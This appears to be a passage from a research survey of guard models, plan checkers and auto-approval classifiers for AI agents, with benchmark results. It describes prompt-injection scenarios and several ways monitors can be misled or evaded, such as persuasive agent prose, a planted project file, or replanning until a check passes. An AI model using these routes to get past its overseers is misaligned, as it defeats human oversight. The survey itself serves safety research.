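Zheng, Li and colleagues (2026), in *StepGuard*, tried to stop a guard from relying on suspicious context. They generated runs in which an agent takes an unsafe action, then kept everything before that action and wrote two safe continuations, one where the agent declines and one where it recognises the risk and continues the task safely. They also generated separate, harmless runs that use the same tools.

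In the customer-file example, one version would email the file to the outsider, and another would ignore the planted instruction and write the summary. Both versions have the same history, so a guard cannot tell them apart by detecting the attack in the file. Similarly, the innocent runs show that an email tool is not dangerous in itself.

After initial training on these examples, StepGuard classified 91% of unsafe examples correctly but only 69% of safe ones. Zheng and colleagues then used reinforcement learning that gave more weight to whichever group had the lower accuracy at the time. This reduced false alarms, raising accuracy on safe examples to 78%, but lowered accuracy on unsafe ones to 86%.

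StepGuard has only 4 billion parameters, but it was slightly more accurate than GPT-5.4 on the AgentDojo calls (95.7% against 93.9%). On the AgentHarm calls, with the controversial cases removed, StepGuard scored 73.8% and GPT-5.4 scored 68.8%. Llama Guard beat both with 82.2%, which is consistent with the labels still depending entirely on whether the request was malicious.

Zheng and colleagues also ran the guards with a live agent based on Qwen3.6-35B. When StepGuard blocks a call, the agent gets a prompt to reconsider but not the guard's reasoning.

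*Results for a live agent, from Zheng and colleagues*

| Guard | AgentDojo: attacks that succeeded | AgentDojo: user's tasks completed | AgentDyn: attacks that succeeded | AgentDyn: user's tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 25.1% | 89.7% | 21.2% | 73.3% |
| TS-Guard | 6.2% | 92.8% | 13.8% | 70.0% |
| StepGuard | 1.2% | 90.7% | 9.3% | 66.7% |

AgentDyn has longer tasks, and some of the third-party instructions in them are helpful, so an agent cannot ignore them all. StepGuard let through far more attacks there and also made the agent complete fewer legitimate tasks. This drop was larger on AgentHarm, where the completion rate for benign tasks fell from 71% to 53%.

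Perhaps the most useful test used 100 recorded runs from a separate NVIDIA dataset, which people had inspected and labelled by what the agent did. StepGuard classified 82 correctly and TS-Guard 56. By calculation, StepGuard caught 44 of the 50 unsafe runs and TS-Guard only 17. The comparison is somewhat unfair because TS-Guard was trained to judge single calls, not complete runs. Still, catching 34% of unsafe runs is far below the 89.5% it scored on AgentDojo.

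StepGuard's false alarms show that matched examples only partly solved the problem. Zheng and colleagues examined all 307 false alarms across their benchmarks. In 134 cases the agent had used a sensitive tool legitimately, and in another 79 it had handled suspicious material safely.

### Newer general-purpose models

A developer can also prompt a general-purpose model to act as the guard. *ToolRosetta* (Demirkiran and Ernstberger, 2026) compared several newer models with the specialised guards on TS-Bench calls.

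*Recall and false-positive rate (FPR) on TS-Bench calls, from Demirkiran and Ernstberger*

| Guard | AgentDojo recall | AgentDojo FPR | AgentHarm recall | AgentHarm FPR |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 98% | 1% | 83% | 17% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 99% | 8% | 89% | 28% |
| StepGuard | 99% | 4% | 83% | 32% |
| TS-Guard | 88% | 8% | 98% | 48% |
| Qwen 3.8 27B | 100% | 35% | 95% | 46% |

Gemini 3.8 Flash has the lowest false-positive rate on both sets without any special training for the task, so GPT-4o's rate of 62% is out of date as a measure of what general models can do. But Qwen 3.8, also a recent model, flagged about a third of the safe AgentDojo calls, so a recent model is not necessarily a good guard.

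Guards that judge whole runs, such as the one in *AgentDoG 1.5*, are hard to compare on TS-Bench. Once an agent has sent a confidential file, such a guard should keep flagging the run, but TS-Bench would count each later flag on a harmless call as a false alarm.

The main experiment in *ToolRosetta* changed how the same action was written. TS-Bench presents calls as a tool name with structured arguments, but coding agents often act through shell commands. When Demirkiran and Ernstberger rewrote the AgentDojo calls as shell commands, TS-Guard's false-positive rate rose from 7.8% to 29%. StepGuard's rate hardly changed, and Gemini's and Claude's error rates moved by at most 3.4 percentage points on either set.

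A guard's ability to read code and structured data may explain some of this. Demirkiran and Ernstberger cite *TraceSafe*, an earlier benchmark by Chen, Huang and colleagues (2026), in which guards' accuracy on tool-call records was more closely related to their skill with structured data than to their resistance to jailbreaks.

A parser of about forty lines restored the original verdicts by turning each command back into a structured call. This worked because a program had produced the commands in a regular format. The parser would not help with a script like `send_notes.py` in the earlier example, which reads its recipient from another file when it runs.

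The language of the request also affects some guards. In *Language Is a Security Surface for Agent Guards*, Demirkiran and Ernstberger (2026) translated only the user's request in each example. Translating one request, about hotels in Paris, into Turkish raised the share of calls that TS-Guard blocked from 12% to 92%. Nemotron Nano 9B, a small general model, lost 7.4 percentage points of recall when the requests were in Amharic. Gemini's verdicts did not change in any of the five languages.

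Gemini's verdicts were stable because the history and the agent's stated reasoning already contained enough information to judge each call. With the user's request removed, Gemini gave the same verdict on every AgentDojo call in all three runs.

A high score on AgentDojo therefore does not show that Gemini can tell an authorised email from an identical unauthorised one, which a guard can do only by using the user's request. Removing the request from the AgentHarm examples lowered Gemini's recall from 83% to 76%, so Gemini does use it in some cases.

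### When unsafe calls are rare

About 29% of the AgentDojo calls in TS-Bench are unsafe. In an ordinary deployment the share should be far lower, and this changes what an alarm means. If π is the share of calls that are unsafe, R is recall and F is the false-positive rate, then:

share of alarms that are real = πR / (πR + (1 − π)F)

Suppose 1 call in 1,000 is unsafe and an agent makes 100,000 calls. At its AgentDojo error rates, TS-Guard would catch about 89 of the 100 unsafe calls and flag 7.4% of the 99,900 safe ones, producing about 7,400 false alarms. Only one alarm in 83 would be real. On the benchmark, where unsafe calls are much more common, 315 of 379 alarms (83%) would be correct at the same error rates.

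*Expected results for 100,000 calls, of which 100 are unsafe, using AgentDojo rates*

| Guard | Unsafe calls caught | False alarms | Alarms that are real |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o, strict threshold | 100 | 62,000 | 1 in 620 |
| TS-Guard | 89 | 7,400 | 1 in 83 |
| StepGuard | 99 | 4,000 | 1 in 41 |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 98 | 1,200 | 1 in 13 |

A person who spent one minute on each TS-Guard alarm would need about 124 hours to review them all. A reviewer who finds 82 false alarms for each real one may start approving calls without reading them. For half of TS-Guard's alarms to be real if its recall stayed the same, its false-positive rate would have to be about 0.09%, roughly one-eightieth of the measured rate.

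The real number of false alarms depends heavily on the agent's work. Some of the safe AgentDojo calls follow an injection, which makes guards more likely to flag them, so ordinary office work might produce fewer false alarms. But if the safe calls resembled those in AgentHarm, TS-Guard's 46% false-positive rate would produce about 46,000 false alarms.

Feedback makes these errors more tolerable because the agent can often find another way to do the task without involving anyone. Developers can also use fixed rules for cases they can describe in advance. In *TACT-Bench* (2026), two versions of a language-model check on a Claude Opus 4.8 agent wrongly blocked 8.2% and 4.3% of benign cases, while hand-written rules wrongly blocked none. But the rules blocked only three of the 232 calls they checked, which may partly explain why they blocked no benign cases.

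### What the labels measure

TS-Bench's unsafe calls all come from malicious requests or prompt injections. None is an overeager action, so TS-Guard's 89.5% recall on the benchmark is not evidence that it would catch overeager actions.

The labels in ASB also depend on a shortcut, the type of tool called. Calls to attack tools count as unsafe or controversial, and calls to normal tools count as safe. About half of the attack tools have openly malicious names or descriptions. One, called "DestructiveMaintenance", has a description that mentions working "without detection". A guard could do well on these cases by reading the tool list, with little understanding of what the call would do.

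Mou and colleagues used GPT-4o to help sort AgentDojo's tools into those that served the user's task and those that served the injected one. They then excluded calls that served the injected task but changed nothing, because the effects of these calls were ambiguous. A call that followed an injection and opened a confidential record would therefore be excluded. Many such lookups count as violations in the GAP benchmark, so a guard that behaves consistently could do well on one benchmark and badly on the other.

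One way to avoid disputed labels is to define a violation by a written policy. *LEANGUARD* (2026) does this with rules in Lean, a programming language for computer-checked proofs. A call is a violation if the rules deny it, which can be checked exactly by replaying the record of a run. But whoever writes the rules must still judge what to deny, and a harmful call they did not anticipate would count as compliant.

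### Training data that resembles the test

TS-Guard's recall on injected calls is highest on ASB, at 94%, but ASB also supplied 1,520 of TS-Guard's 2,193 training examples. The training and test examples come from different fields. Mou and colleagues also checked for near-duplicates by representing each request and its tool descriptions as a vector, and found no test example with a similarity of 0.9 or more to a training example.

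That check is good at finding copied tasks, but it could miss wording that different attacks share. Several of ASB's published examples introduce the injected task with the same sentence, which says that the agent "must strictly adhere to the following instruction". A guard that learned to recognise this sentence in one field would also recognise it in another. The shell-command experiment gives some reason for concern, because rewriting the calls raised TS-Guard's false-positive rate on ASB by 38 percentage points, more than on either of the other two sets.

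To test for overlap more directly, Zheng and colleagues removed 186 of StepGuard's 3,000 initial training examples because their tools closely resembled those in the test sets, then retrained the guard. Accuracy rose from 91.3% to 94.3% on AgentDojo calls and fell from 73.8% to 71.4% on AgentHarm calls, so familiar tools probably do not explain the results. In another experiment, they trained the guard on two sources of risk and tested it on six others. It classified 74.9% of those cases correctly, compared with 49.6% for the model before training and 76.8% for a version trained on all eight sources.

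This is good evidence that StepGuard learned something more general than its training examples. However, language models generated and labelled those examples, and the attacks in the tests were fixed in advance. Zheng and colleagues say they did not test adversaries who adapt to the guard. StepGuard's model is public, so an attacker could reword an injection until the guard allowed the resulting call.

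## Checking a whole plan before it runs

Steps that are harmless individually can be harmful as a sequence. Suppose an employee asks an agent to organise a customer event, and the agent writes the following plan.

*Constructed example: a plan for a customer event*

1. Create a shared folder called "Spring event".
2. Save the guest list in the folder, with each customer's phone number and account notes.
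3. Give the outside caterer access to the folder, so they can read the menu.

Each step is ordinary office work, but together they give a caterer the customers' account notes. A check that covers only the third call finds just a request to share an event folder with a supplier. A check that also covers the history could catch the problem at that call, and a plan check could catch it before the agent creates the folder.

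Checking a whole plan before it runs matters most when a half-finished task is worse than one never started. Suppose an agent plans to cancel a company's insurance and then buy a cheaper policy. If a check on each step allows the cancellation but blocks the purchase, the company has no insurance.

### A guard model that reads the plan

*Building a Foundational Guardrail for General Agentic Systems via Synthetic Data* (Huang, Hua and colleagues, 2025) describes Safiron, a guard model with 8 billion parameters, trained to read an agent's full list of intended actions before any of them runs. It labels the plan harmless or risky, assigns one of eight risk categories (such as privacy violations or financial loss), and gives a short explanation. Agents write plans in many formats, from XML to bullet points, so a separate adapter model first converts each plan to a common format.

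Records of real harmful plans are scarce, so Huang and colleagues generated about 20,000 training examples with a system they call AuraGen. A language model writes a user request and a harmless plan for it, then inserts a risk in one of four ways:

- It changes a single action.
- It replaces several consecutive actions.
- It abandons the task partway and adds a harmful ending.
- It adds a harmful detour, then returns to the original final action.

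Safiron first learned to imitate the labelled examples. Reinforcement learning then gave it full reward for recognising a harmless plan or naming the right category of a risky one, and half for detecting a risk but naming the wrong category. The mix of examples mattered more than their number. Changing the ratio of harmless to harmful examples from 3:1 to 1:4 raised detection by 15 to 20 percentage points, while growing the training set from 2,000 to 10,000 examples often added only 2 to 5.

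The test set, Pre-Exec Bench, has 1,001 harmless plans and 671 risky ones. Eight open-weight models wrote them, and all three human reviewers had to approve each pair. The table labels the paper's "harmful detection precision" as recall because its formula is the one for recall. The false-positive rates are calculated from the published accuracy and recall.

*Results on Pre-Exec Bench, from Huang and colleagues*

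| Guard | Accuracy | Recall | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Safiron | 94.9% | 97% | 7% |
| DeepSeek-V3 | 65.2% | 60% | 31% |
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet | 62.3% | 79% | 49% |
| GPT-4o | 60.6% | 82% | 54% |
| GPT-5 | 42.5% | 99% | 95% |

A check that allowed every plan would be right 59.9% of the time, so GPT-5 did much worse than no check. It probably applied a different standard from the labels, since it is unlikely to understand plans this badly. A plan is labelled risky only if a model inserted a risk into it, so any objection to an unedited plan counts as a false alarm.

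Safiron, by contrast, was trained on plans edited in the same four ways as the test plans, so it may have learned to recognise the editing as well as the danger. A smaller test partly addresses this concern, using plans that two experts edited by hand for two multi-agent systems, with 50 harmful and 50 harmless plans for each system. Safiron's accuracy with the adapter was lower than on the main benchmark but above 90%.

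Safiron did far worse on single steps. When Mou and colleagues ran it on TS-Bench, it caught 32% of the unsafe calls in AgentHarm, 33% in ASB and 56% in AgentDojo. Its accuracy on AgentDojo was 71.0%, slightly below that of allowing every call. The test is unfair to a plan guard, since a record of past calls and results looks quite different from a list of intended actions. Still, a company can't assume that a guard for plans will also work on tool calls.

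### Plans that a program can verify

A guard model can always misread a plan. If the plan is written in a simple enough language, an ordinary program can instead trace where every piece of data will go. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) presents a system that does this before the first tool call.

SPA's best-known forerunner is CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues presented in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). In CaMeL, one model turns the user's request into code without reading any tool's results. A second model, which has no tools, reads the untrusted content and extracts values for the code to use. An instruction planted in a web page therefore can't rewrite the code. Each value also carries a record of its origin and of who may receive it, and CaMeL checks this record against the tool's rules at every call.

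CaMeL's plans are written in a restricted form of Python. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* has an enterprise-minded follow-up, *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025), which objects that this subset keeps features of Python, such as dynamic typing, that make it difficult to analyse a plan without running it. SPA uses a much smaller language. It handles a request as follows:

1. A planner model reads the request, the list of tools and short descriptions of any stored results from earlier requests. It writes a complete plan.
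2. A program checks that the plan is well formed.
3. The program labels every value the plan will produce and tests each step against the rules for its tool.
4. If every step passes, an interpreter runs the plan exactly as written. If any step fails, nothing runs, and the planner doesn't get a second attempt.

The language has six kinds of step. A plan can retrieve a stored result, call a tool, process text with a model that has no tools, display something to the user, branch on a condition, or loop over a list. It can't do arithmetic or define functions, so the source of every argument is explicit.

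Each value has a confidentiality label, for how secret it is, and an integrity label, for how far the system trusts it. When a step combines several values, the result gets the highest confidentiality and the lowest integrity among them. Data may flow from a source s to a destination d only if

C(s) ≤ C(d) and I(s) ≥ I(d)

The first condition keeps secrets away from tools that are not cleared to receive them. The second keeps untrusted data from controlling sensitive actions.

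Suppose an employee asks an agent to email a renewal reminder to the contact named in customer 4417's file. The listing shows a possible plan in a simplified version of SPA's format.

*Constructed example: a plan that a program can check*

```json
{
  "steps": [
    {
      "type": "tool",
      "name": "read_file",
      "args": {"customer": "4417"},
      "output": "file"
    },
    {
      "type": "q-llm",
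      "inputs": ["file"],
      "prompt": "Extract the contact's email address",
      "output": "address"
    },
    {
      "type": "tool",
      "name": "send_email",
      "args": {
        "to": {"variable": "address"},
        "body": "Your contract renews in March."
      }
    }
  ]
}
```

Suppose the company labels customer files confidential and untrusted, because outsiders write parts of them. Its email tool accepts only public data and requires trusted inputs. The first step passes, and `file` gets both labels. The second step also passes, because the model that extracts the address can't take actions, but `address` inherits the file's labels. The third step breaks both of the email tool's conditions, so the program rejects the plan before the agent opens the file.

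This stops an attacker who has put their own address in the file, but it also blocks an honest employee's reasonable request. The employee could type the address into the request, which SPA treats as trusted, though the agent would then save them less work.

If a plan sends a fixed message to a fixed address only when the customer file contains the word "urgent", whoever wrote the file controls whether the agent sends the message. SPA therefore also gives every step inside a conditional branch the label of the condition.

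Girrens and Wang tested SPA with GPT-5.4-nano on AgentDojo's 97 tasks and 949 prompt-injection attempts.

*Results on AgentDojo, from Girrens and Wang*

| Configuration | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed, under attack | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fixed plan | 53.0% | 54.7% | 0.4% |
| Fixed plan and labels | 29.0% | 29.5% | 0.0% |
| Fixed plan, tool descriptions hidden | 14.1% | 11.7% | 0.0% |
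| Fixed plan and labels, tool descriptions hidden | 6.7% | 8.9% | 0.0% |

Fixing the plan in advance stopped all but four of the attacks. The labels stopped those four, but they also caused the program to reject about 53% of runs and lowered task completion by 24 percentage points. These numbers alone make the labels look less useful than they are, because the attacks in this benchmark mostly work by planting instructions, which a fixed plan already resists. Labels are more useful against planted values, such as a false bank account number on an invoice that the user wants to pay.

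Hiding the tool descriptions from the planner protects it from deceptive ones. The planner then invents the tools it needs, and the software looks for installed tools that match. It found no match in about three-quarters of runs, so this version is not yet usable.

The labels caused a similar drop in completion, from 62.5% to 35.3%, when Girrens and Wang spread each task over several requests. Hiding the contents of stored results from the planner had a much smaller effect. Without labels, the planner still retrieved the right result 95% of the time when an earlier request had stored one, and showing it the contents raised completion by only 3.4 points.

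### What the program guarantees

If the labels and the tool rules are correct, no untrusted value can reach a tool that requires trusted input, however cleverly an attacker words it. Guard models offer no comparable guarantee, because a model's recall on known attacks is weak evidence of its recall on new ones. But the company has to write the labels and rules, and a mistake in them can let an unsafe plan through.

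The guarantee covers where data goes, so a permitted action can still be unwise. Suppose an employee asks an agent to tidy the "2019 projects" folder, and the planner writes a plan that deletes it. The folder's name appears in the plan as a fixed value, and SPA trusts fixed values as much as the user's request because the planner has read only trusted material. The deletion therefore passes the check, although the employee never asked for it.

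SPA treats the planner's choices as if the user had made them. That is reasonable when the only danger is an outside attacker, which is the case Girrens and Wang address. They exclude failures of the model itself. Guarding against an overeager or misaligned planner would require a different check, such as a rule that every deletion needs approval.

### Evidence from robot planning

Robots often receive plans as explicit lists of actions, so researchers can measure how safe the plans are without running them. *Using large language models for embodied planning introduces systematic safety risks* (Zhang, Qu and colleagues, 2026) presents DESPITE, a benchmark of 12,279 tasks written in a formal language that specifies the conditions and effects of every action.

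Some actions are dangerous only in certain conditions, such as putting a knife on a table when a child is near it. The model that writes the plan receives a description of the scene, including the child, but not the danger rules. An ordinary program then checks the plan against those rules and adds one to a counter for each dangerous action. The plan is safe if the counter is still zero at the end. Because an ordinary program does the checking, the verdict does not depend on another model's judgment.

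Zhang and colleagues tested 23 models on 1,044 of the harder tasks. Gemini 3 Pro Preview, the best planner, failed to produce a working plan for only 0.4% of them, but about 28% of its plans were dangerous. GPT-5 at its highest reasoning setting was the safest model, but nearly one in five of its working plans was dangerous. About half of Claude Sonnet 4.5's working plans were dangerous.

The researchers separated planning ability F, the share of plans that reach the goal, from safety awareness A, the share that avoid danger whether or not they work. The share of plans that are both safe and successful is then roughly

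S ≈ F × A

Between Llama 3.2 3B and Llama 3.1 405B, F rose from 0.5% to 52.5%, but A only from 41% to 52%. By this formula, S rose from 0.2% to about 27%. Nearly all of this apparent gain in safety comes from the larger model producing more plans that work. Across the 18 open-weight models, a tenfold increase in size added about 27 points to planning ability and 4.5 to safety awareness.

Three proprietary reasoning models did better, with awareness between 71% and 81%. These models are all from 2025, and current ones may be safer. The result is a reason not to treat competence as evidence of safety, especially for privacy violations and breaches of social norms. Tasks involving these risks had shorter plans than tasks with physical dangers, but they made up a growing share as danger became harder to avoid.

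DESPITE's checker catches every dangerous plan because people wrote down the dangers beforehand. When nobody has done that, a model must judge the plan. *PlanGuard* (Chen, Miao and colleagues, 2026) trained small guard models for this and tested them on 50 pairs of plans. In each unsafe plan, every step looks safe by itself. For example, a robot turns on a burner and later puts napkins beside the stove.

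The published scores imply that the larger guard caught 30 of the 50 unsafe plans when it judged each step separately and 44 when it read the whole plan. It also flagged 24 and 27 of the safe plans, respectively. Reading the whole plan helped, but a guard that flags about half of safe plans isn't ready for use. The comparison also favours whole plans, because the guard judged every step against a picture of the kitchen from before the robot had done anything. A check during execution could detect that the burner was already on.

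Models may also judge single actions well and still write unsafe plans. In *CAPSafe*, Farag, Stoyanchev and colleagues (2026) tested nine models on both tasks. Qwen3-32B recognised 92% of unsafe actions, but only 28% of its plans for household tasks were free of hazards. For Gemini 3 Pro, the figures were 99% and 37%.

Part of this gap arises because a safe plan must avoid every hazard in the scene. The scenes contained 12 potential hazards on average, and a model that avoids each one with probability 0.918 avoids all 12 only about 36% of the time, which is close to Qwen's result. Gemini's plans were hazard-free much less often than the 91% that the same calculation predicts from its judgments of single actions. The likely reason is that the prompt for single actions mentioned safety and the basic planning prompt did not. With safety guidelines and examples of careful plans, Gemini's hazard-free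 share rose to 79%.

### When the agent changes its plan

All of these checks depend on the agent carrying out the approved plan. Many agents revise their plans after each result, and some depart from a plan without saying so. In *From Plan to Action*, Liu, Dehghan and colleagues (2026) studied 21,120 runs of a coding agent under eight variations of the plan it was told to follow. Periodic reminders of the plan reduced violations and helped the agent solve more problems. But the agent did worse with a poor plan than with no plan, so forcing an agent to follow its plan does not always help.

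Standard measures of whether agents follow their plans are of little use for safety. The scoring guide in *Do LLM Agents Execute the Plans They Declare?* (2026) counts how many planned steps the agent completed. Extra actions don't affect the score unless they replace or prevent a planned step. That is sensible for measuring reliability, but an agent that planned to read and summarize a customer's file could get full marks even if it then emailed the file to a stranger.

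SPA handles this by forbidding revision. A plan can include branches for events the planner expects, but if a tool fails or returns data in the wrong form, the request ends. Girrens and Wang did not test a version that could replan, so we don't know how much this rule alone reduces performance. The reduction is probably small when the planner has all the facts at the start. Farag and colleagues found no significant improvement in preliminary tests where models planned one step at a time, and they suggest that this was because their models had a full description of the scene. The reduction would be larger for an agent that has to read a customer's file to find out what to do next.

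A more flexible approach is to check each revised plan, which lets the agent adapt as it works. In *PSG-Agent* (2025), a monitor passes the plan, adds limits to it, or sends it back for replanning. But each new check can raise another false alarm. At Safiron's false-positive rate of about 7%, five checks of harmless plans would produce at least one false alarm about 29% of the time, if the errors were independent. The agent also writes its revisions after reading outside material, so an attacker may have influenced them. And if the agent can keep revising until a plan passes, it may eventually find an unsafe plan that the check misses, which is one reason SPA allows only one attempt.

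Farag and colleagues had each of nine models check its own plan for hazards once and revise it before execution. This lowered task completion in all nine. The share of tasks completed without any hazard rose in four models and fell in the other five.

The third option is to compare each action with the approved plan. *PSG-Agent* does this in part. It uses the plan to set limits on tool arguments and on how often the agent may call a tool, and a separate component enforces these limits at every call. A stricter version could tell an authorised email from an identical unauthorised one, because the approved plan would include only the email the employee asked for. A classifier that reads only the call cannot make this distinction. The comparison works only if the agent wrote the plan before it read the customer's file, since an instruction planted in the file could otherwise lead the agent to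 include the unauthorised email in the plan.

The plan must also be specific enough to limit the agent, but not so specific that it blocks harmless corrections. "Brief the attendees" would permit almost any email, while a list of exact calls would block an agent that has to search again after misspelling a name. *OSGuard* (2026) doesn't need a detailed plan because it compares each action with the user's original instruction. Its guard blocks actions that are unsafe or unrelated to the instruction and explains why, and the agent then proposes another action.

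None of these sources measures how many more tasks an agent fails when software makes it follow an approved plan. The closest evidence comes from Mou and colleagues, whose step checks intervene at the same point but test whether a step is safe rather than whether it matches a plan.

*Measured effect on completed tasks*

| Intervention | Model | Before | After |
|---|---|---|---|
| Adding SPA's labels to a fixed plan | GPT-5.4-nano | 53.0% | 29.0% |
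| Reviewing the plan once before execution | GPT-5-mini | 79.8% | 60.9% |
| Reviewing the plan once before execution | Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 82.3% | 78.6% |
| Reviewing the plan once before execution | Gemini 3 Pro | 93.8% | 90.1% |
| Ending the run when a step check finds a problem | Qwen2.5-14B | 42.6% | 36.5% |
| Returning feedback when a step check finds a problem | Qwen2.5-14B | 42.6% | 42.7% |

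The tasks differ too much to rank the methods by these numbers. But the last two rows use the same guard model, agent and tasks, and returning feedback again does better than ending the run. An agent that departs from its plan for a good reason could explain the change and ask for approval, but this protects the user only if the approver sometimes refuses.

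## Action reviewers in deployed coding agents

People asked to approve an agent's individual actions seldom refuse. Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans the agent presents but only 3% of its requests to take individual actions, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). Anthropic attributes the low rate for actions to approval fatigue, in which a developer who sees dozens of prompts a day stops reading them.

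These rates alone are weak evidence of fatigue. Most requests concern safe commands, so an attentive user would also approve nearly all of them, and a user may reject a plan because they prefer another design. Users' efforts to avoid the prompts are stronger evidence. In Anthropic's data, 62% of users had bypassed permission checks or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands, and a quarter of interactive sessions started with the checks off. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen et al., 2026) describes the same habit at OpenAI, where a sizable minority of Codex users had pre-approved every command beginning with "python". A Python script can do almost anything, so that rule removes much of the protection.

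Anthropic and OpenAI now let users have a language model review a coding agent's actions for them. Anthropic calls this feature auto mode, and OpenAI calls it Auto-review.

### The route of a tool call through auto mode

Auto mode began as a research preview in March 2026, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* (2026), and became the default on individual and team plans in August. In recent versions, all interactive sessions in a terminal or the VS Code editor start in auto mode unless the user or their company has chosen another mode. Scripted runs still start with manual approval, according to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026), which describes the software as of 12 November.

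Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode* and the company's March engineering post together describe the route of a tool call:

1. Claude Code applies the user's own rules, which can allow a call, block it or require a prompt. It suspends very broad permissions, such as one for every Python command.
2. File reads and edits inside the project folder run without review, apart from edits to a few sensitive files such as the agent's own settings.
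3. Most other calls go to a classifier, which is a language model with a long prompt. It first answers yes or no in a single token, under an instruction to "err on the side of blocking".
4. If the answer is to block, the same model receives the same prompt again with an instruction to reason carefully. It can then clear the call.
5. If the model still blocks the call, the agent receives the denial and looks for a safer way to continue. After three denials in a row, or 20 in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user.

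Step 2 relies on version control to undo a bad edit, which doesn't help with work that the user never committed.

The classifier's prompt lists what to block, such as sending internal data outside or disabling logs, along with some narrow exceptions. It also has rules for interpreting the user's wishes: anything the agent decides for itself is unauthorised until the user says otherwise, and a question such as "can we fix this?" is not an instruction.

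The classifier's prompt includes an instruction to judge a command by its effect, so if the agent writes a script and then runs it, the classifier should evaluate the script. In the earlier example, it could read `send_notes.py` because the call that created the script is part of the record. If `meeting.json` already existed, however, the classifier could not read the recipient, because it does not receive the contents of files the agent opens.

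A task can continue after a denial. In one case at Anthropic, a report failed to upload to an internal drive, and Claude tried to publish it on a public code-sharing site. Auto mode blocked this and asked the user what to do. In most sessions, however, the agent now receives only the fixed text "Blocked by classifier". Fuller feedback may protect the agent better, as it did in Mou and colleagues' tests.

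### Why the classifier doesn't receive everything

Claude Code removes the agent's prose from the record before passing it to the classifier. Anthropic's reason is that the agent might otherwise persuade the classifier to make a bad decision, for example by writing that the user had implicitly approved a deletion. Claude Code also removes tool results, because prompt injections enter through them. The classifier therefore receives mainly the user's messages and the tool calls.

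In the customer-file example, the classifier would receive the request for a summary and the email to an outside address. That should be enough for it to block the email, whatever led the agent to try to send it.

The drawback is that the classifier often can't determine where a value came from. Suppose the employee asks the agent to send the file to the customer's lawyer, and the agent takes the lawyer's address from the file. The classifier receives an address that the employee never typed. It can't determine whether the address belongs to the lawyer or to an attacker who edited the file, or whether the agent made it up.

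Anthropic has dealt with one version of this problem by having the classifier block any command that deletes a folder whose name came only from earlier command output. The agent can try again with the full path written out, which the classifier can then check.

Anthropic also tested the classifier with other inputs. Adding the agent's prose and the tool results made it worse at catching overeager actions, perhaps because a longer record gives the agent's framing more influence. When it received only tool calls, it missed the fewest dangerous actions, but it blocked actions users had clearly requested because it could not distinguish an authorised call from an identical unauthorised one.

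Since March, Anthropic has given the classifier some context that the agent doesn't write during the session. Before a command that could discard uncommitted work, Claude Code checks whether there is any and passes the result to the classifier. The classifier is also given information on whether code is about to go to a public or a private repository. It also receives the project's file of standing instructions, CLAUDE.md. This is useful, but presumably a repository from an untrusted source could include a CLAUDE.md written to influence the classifier.

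A separate probe scans tool results for injections before the agent reads them, and adds a warning if it finds one. An injection succeeds only if the agent follows it despite any warning and the resulting call looks authorised to a classifier that never read the injection.

If a user tells Claude Code "don't push", its classifier should block any attempt to upload code, even one it would normally allow. But Claude Code shortens the record when a conversation gets too long, which may remove the user's message. Anthropic recommends a fixed deny rule for anything that must never happen.

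### The March results

Anthropic tested the classifier on three sets of actions: 10,000 real tool calls by its employees, 52 real overeager actions, and 1,000 synthetic attempts to leak data.

*Auto mode's error rates in March 2026, from Anthropic*

| Stage | Real calls blocked wrongly | Overeager actions missed | Synthetic leaks missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fast filter alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
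| Filter, then reasoning | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The reasoning stage reviews only calls the filter has flagged, so it can release a call but cannot catch one the filter missed. By calculation, it released about 810 of the filter's 850 false alarms. It also released about five of the roughly 49 overeager actions the filter had caught, and 39 of the 982 leaks.

An agent that makes 40 safe calls has about a 15% chance of at least one wrongful block at a false-positive rate of 0.4%, compared with 87% at the 5% rate in the earlier example, if the errors are independent. If 1 call in 1,000 were unsafe, about one block in six would be correct at these rates, compared with the one in 83 calculated for TS-Guard from its AgentDojo results. The two calculations use different kinds of calls, so they don't show how the checks would compare on the same work.

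The 17% miss rate for overeager actions is much less certain. It is based on about nine misses in 52 cases, which gives a 95% interval of roughly 9% to 30%. The sample also includes only actions that somebody noticed, either because an employee refused them or because Anthropic flagged them later. Overeager actions that nobody noticed may well be harder for a classifier to catch too.

Even so, these 52 cases are unusually valuable, since TS-Bench contains no overeager actions.

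### Taking a vague request as consent

In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier identified the danger but wrongly inferred that the user had agreed to it.

For example, a user might ask the agent to "clean up the PR" (pull request, a set of proposed code changes). The agent then force-pushes, which replaces the history of a shared branch and may delete a colleague's work. The classifier correctly identifies the force-push as dangerous but allows it because the user's request seems related. In other cases, the user had approved a similar action earlier, and the classifier treated that approval as permission for the new one.

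Anthropic tried to fix this by changing the prompt but found no change whose benefits outweighed its drawbacks. The difficulty is understandable, since users rarely name every command they want. Someone who asks an agent to "fix the failing tests" has agreed to dozens of small actions without listing them, and requiring explicit consent for each would bring back the requests for approval.

Users can help by being specific about the risky part of a request. *Explicit authorization scope improves LLM-based permission checking in coding agents* (2026) found that making the scope of a permission explicit improves this kind of check. Several of auto mode's current rules require such specificity. For instance, it blocks the deletion of some resources unless the user has named them.

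A test of auto mode in *Ajar* (2026) suggests that, because the classifier relies on the user's words, instructions that a user pastes in from a website could gain the user's own authority. The test put each proposed call in the system prompt and recorded whether the classifier allowed it. When the same instructions appeared in the user's message instead, auto mode allowed every call. However, the calls may not have included any that Anthropic says the classifier should never approve, such as sending secrets outside.

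### Testers and classifier on the same commands

In an August post, Anthropic argues that auto mode is at least as safe as an ordinary user clicking through prompts. Its main evidence is an experiment with 1,053 professional testers it hired through a research vendor. The testers did coding work in a test environment and knew they were being evaluated, but not on what. Partway through each session, the software replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. The dangerous command did not run even if the tester approved it.

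The testers refused 143 of the 1,053 commands (13.6%). Auto mode blocked 937 of the same commands (89%).

*Decisions on 1,053 dangerous commands, calculated from Anthropic's figures*

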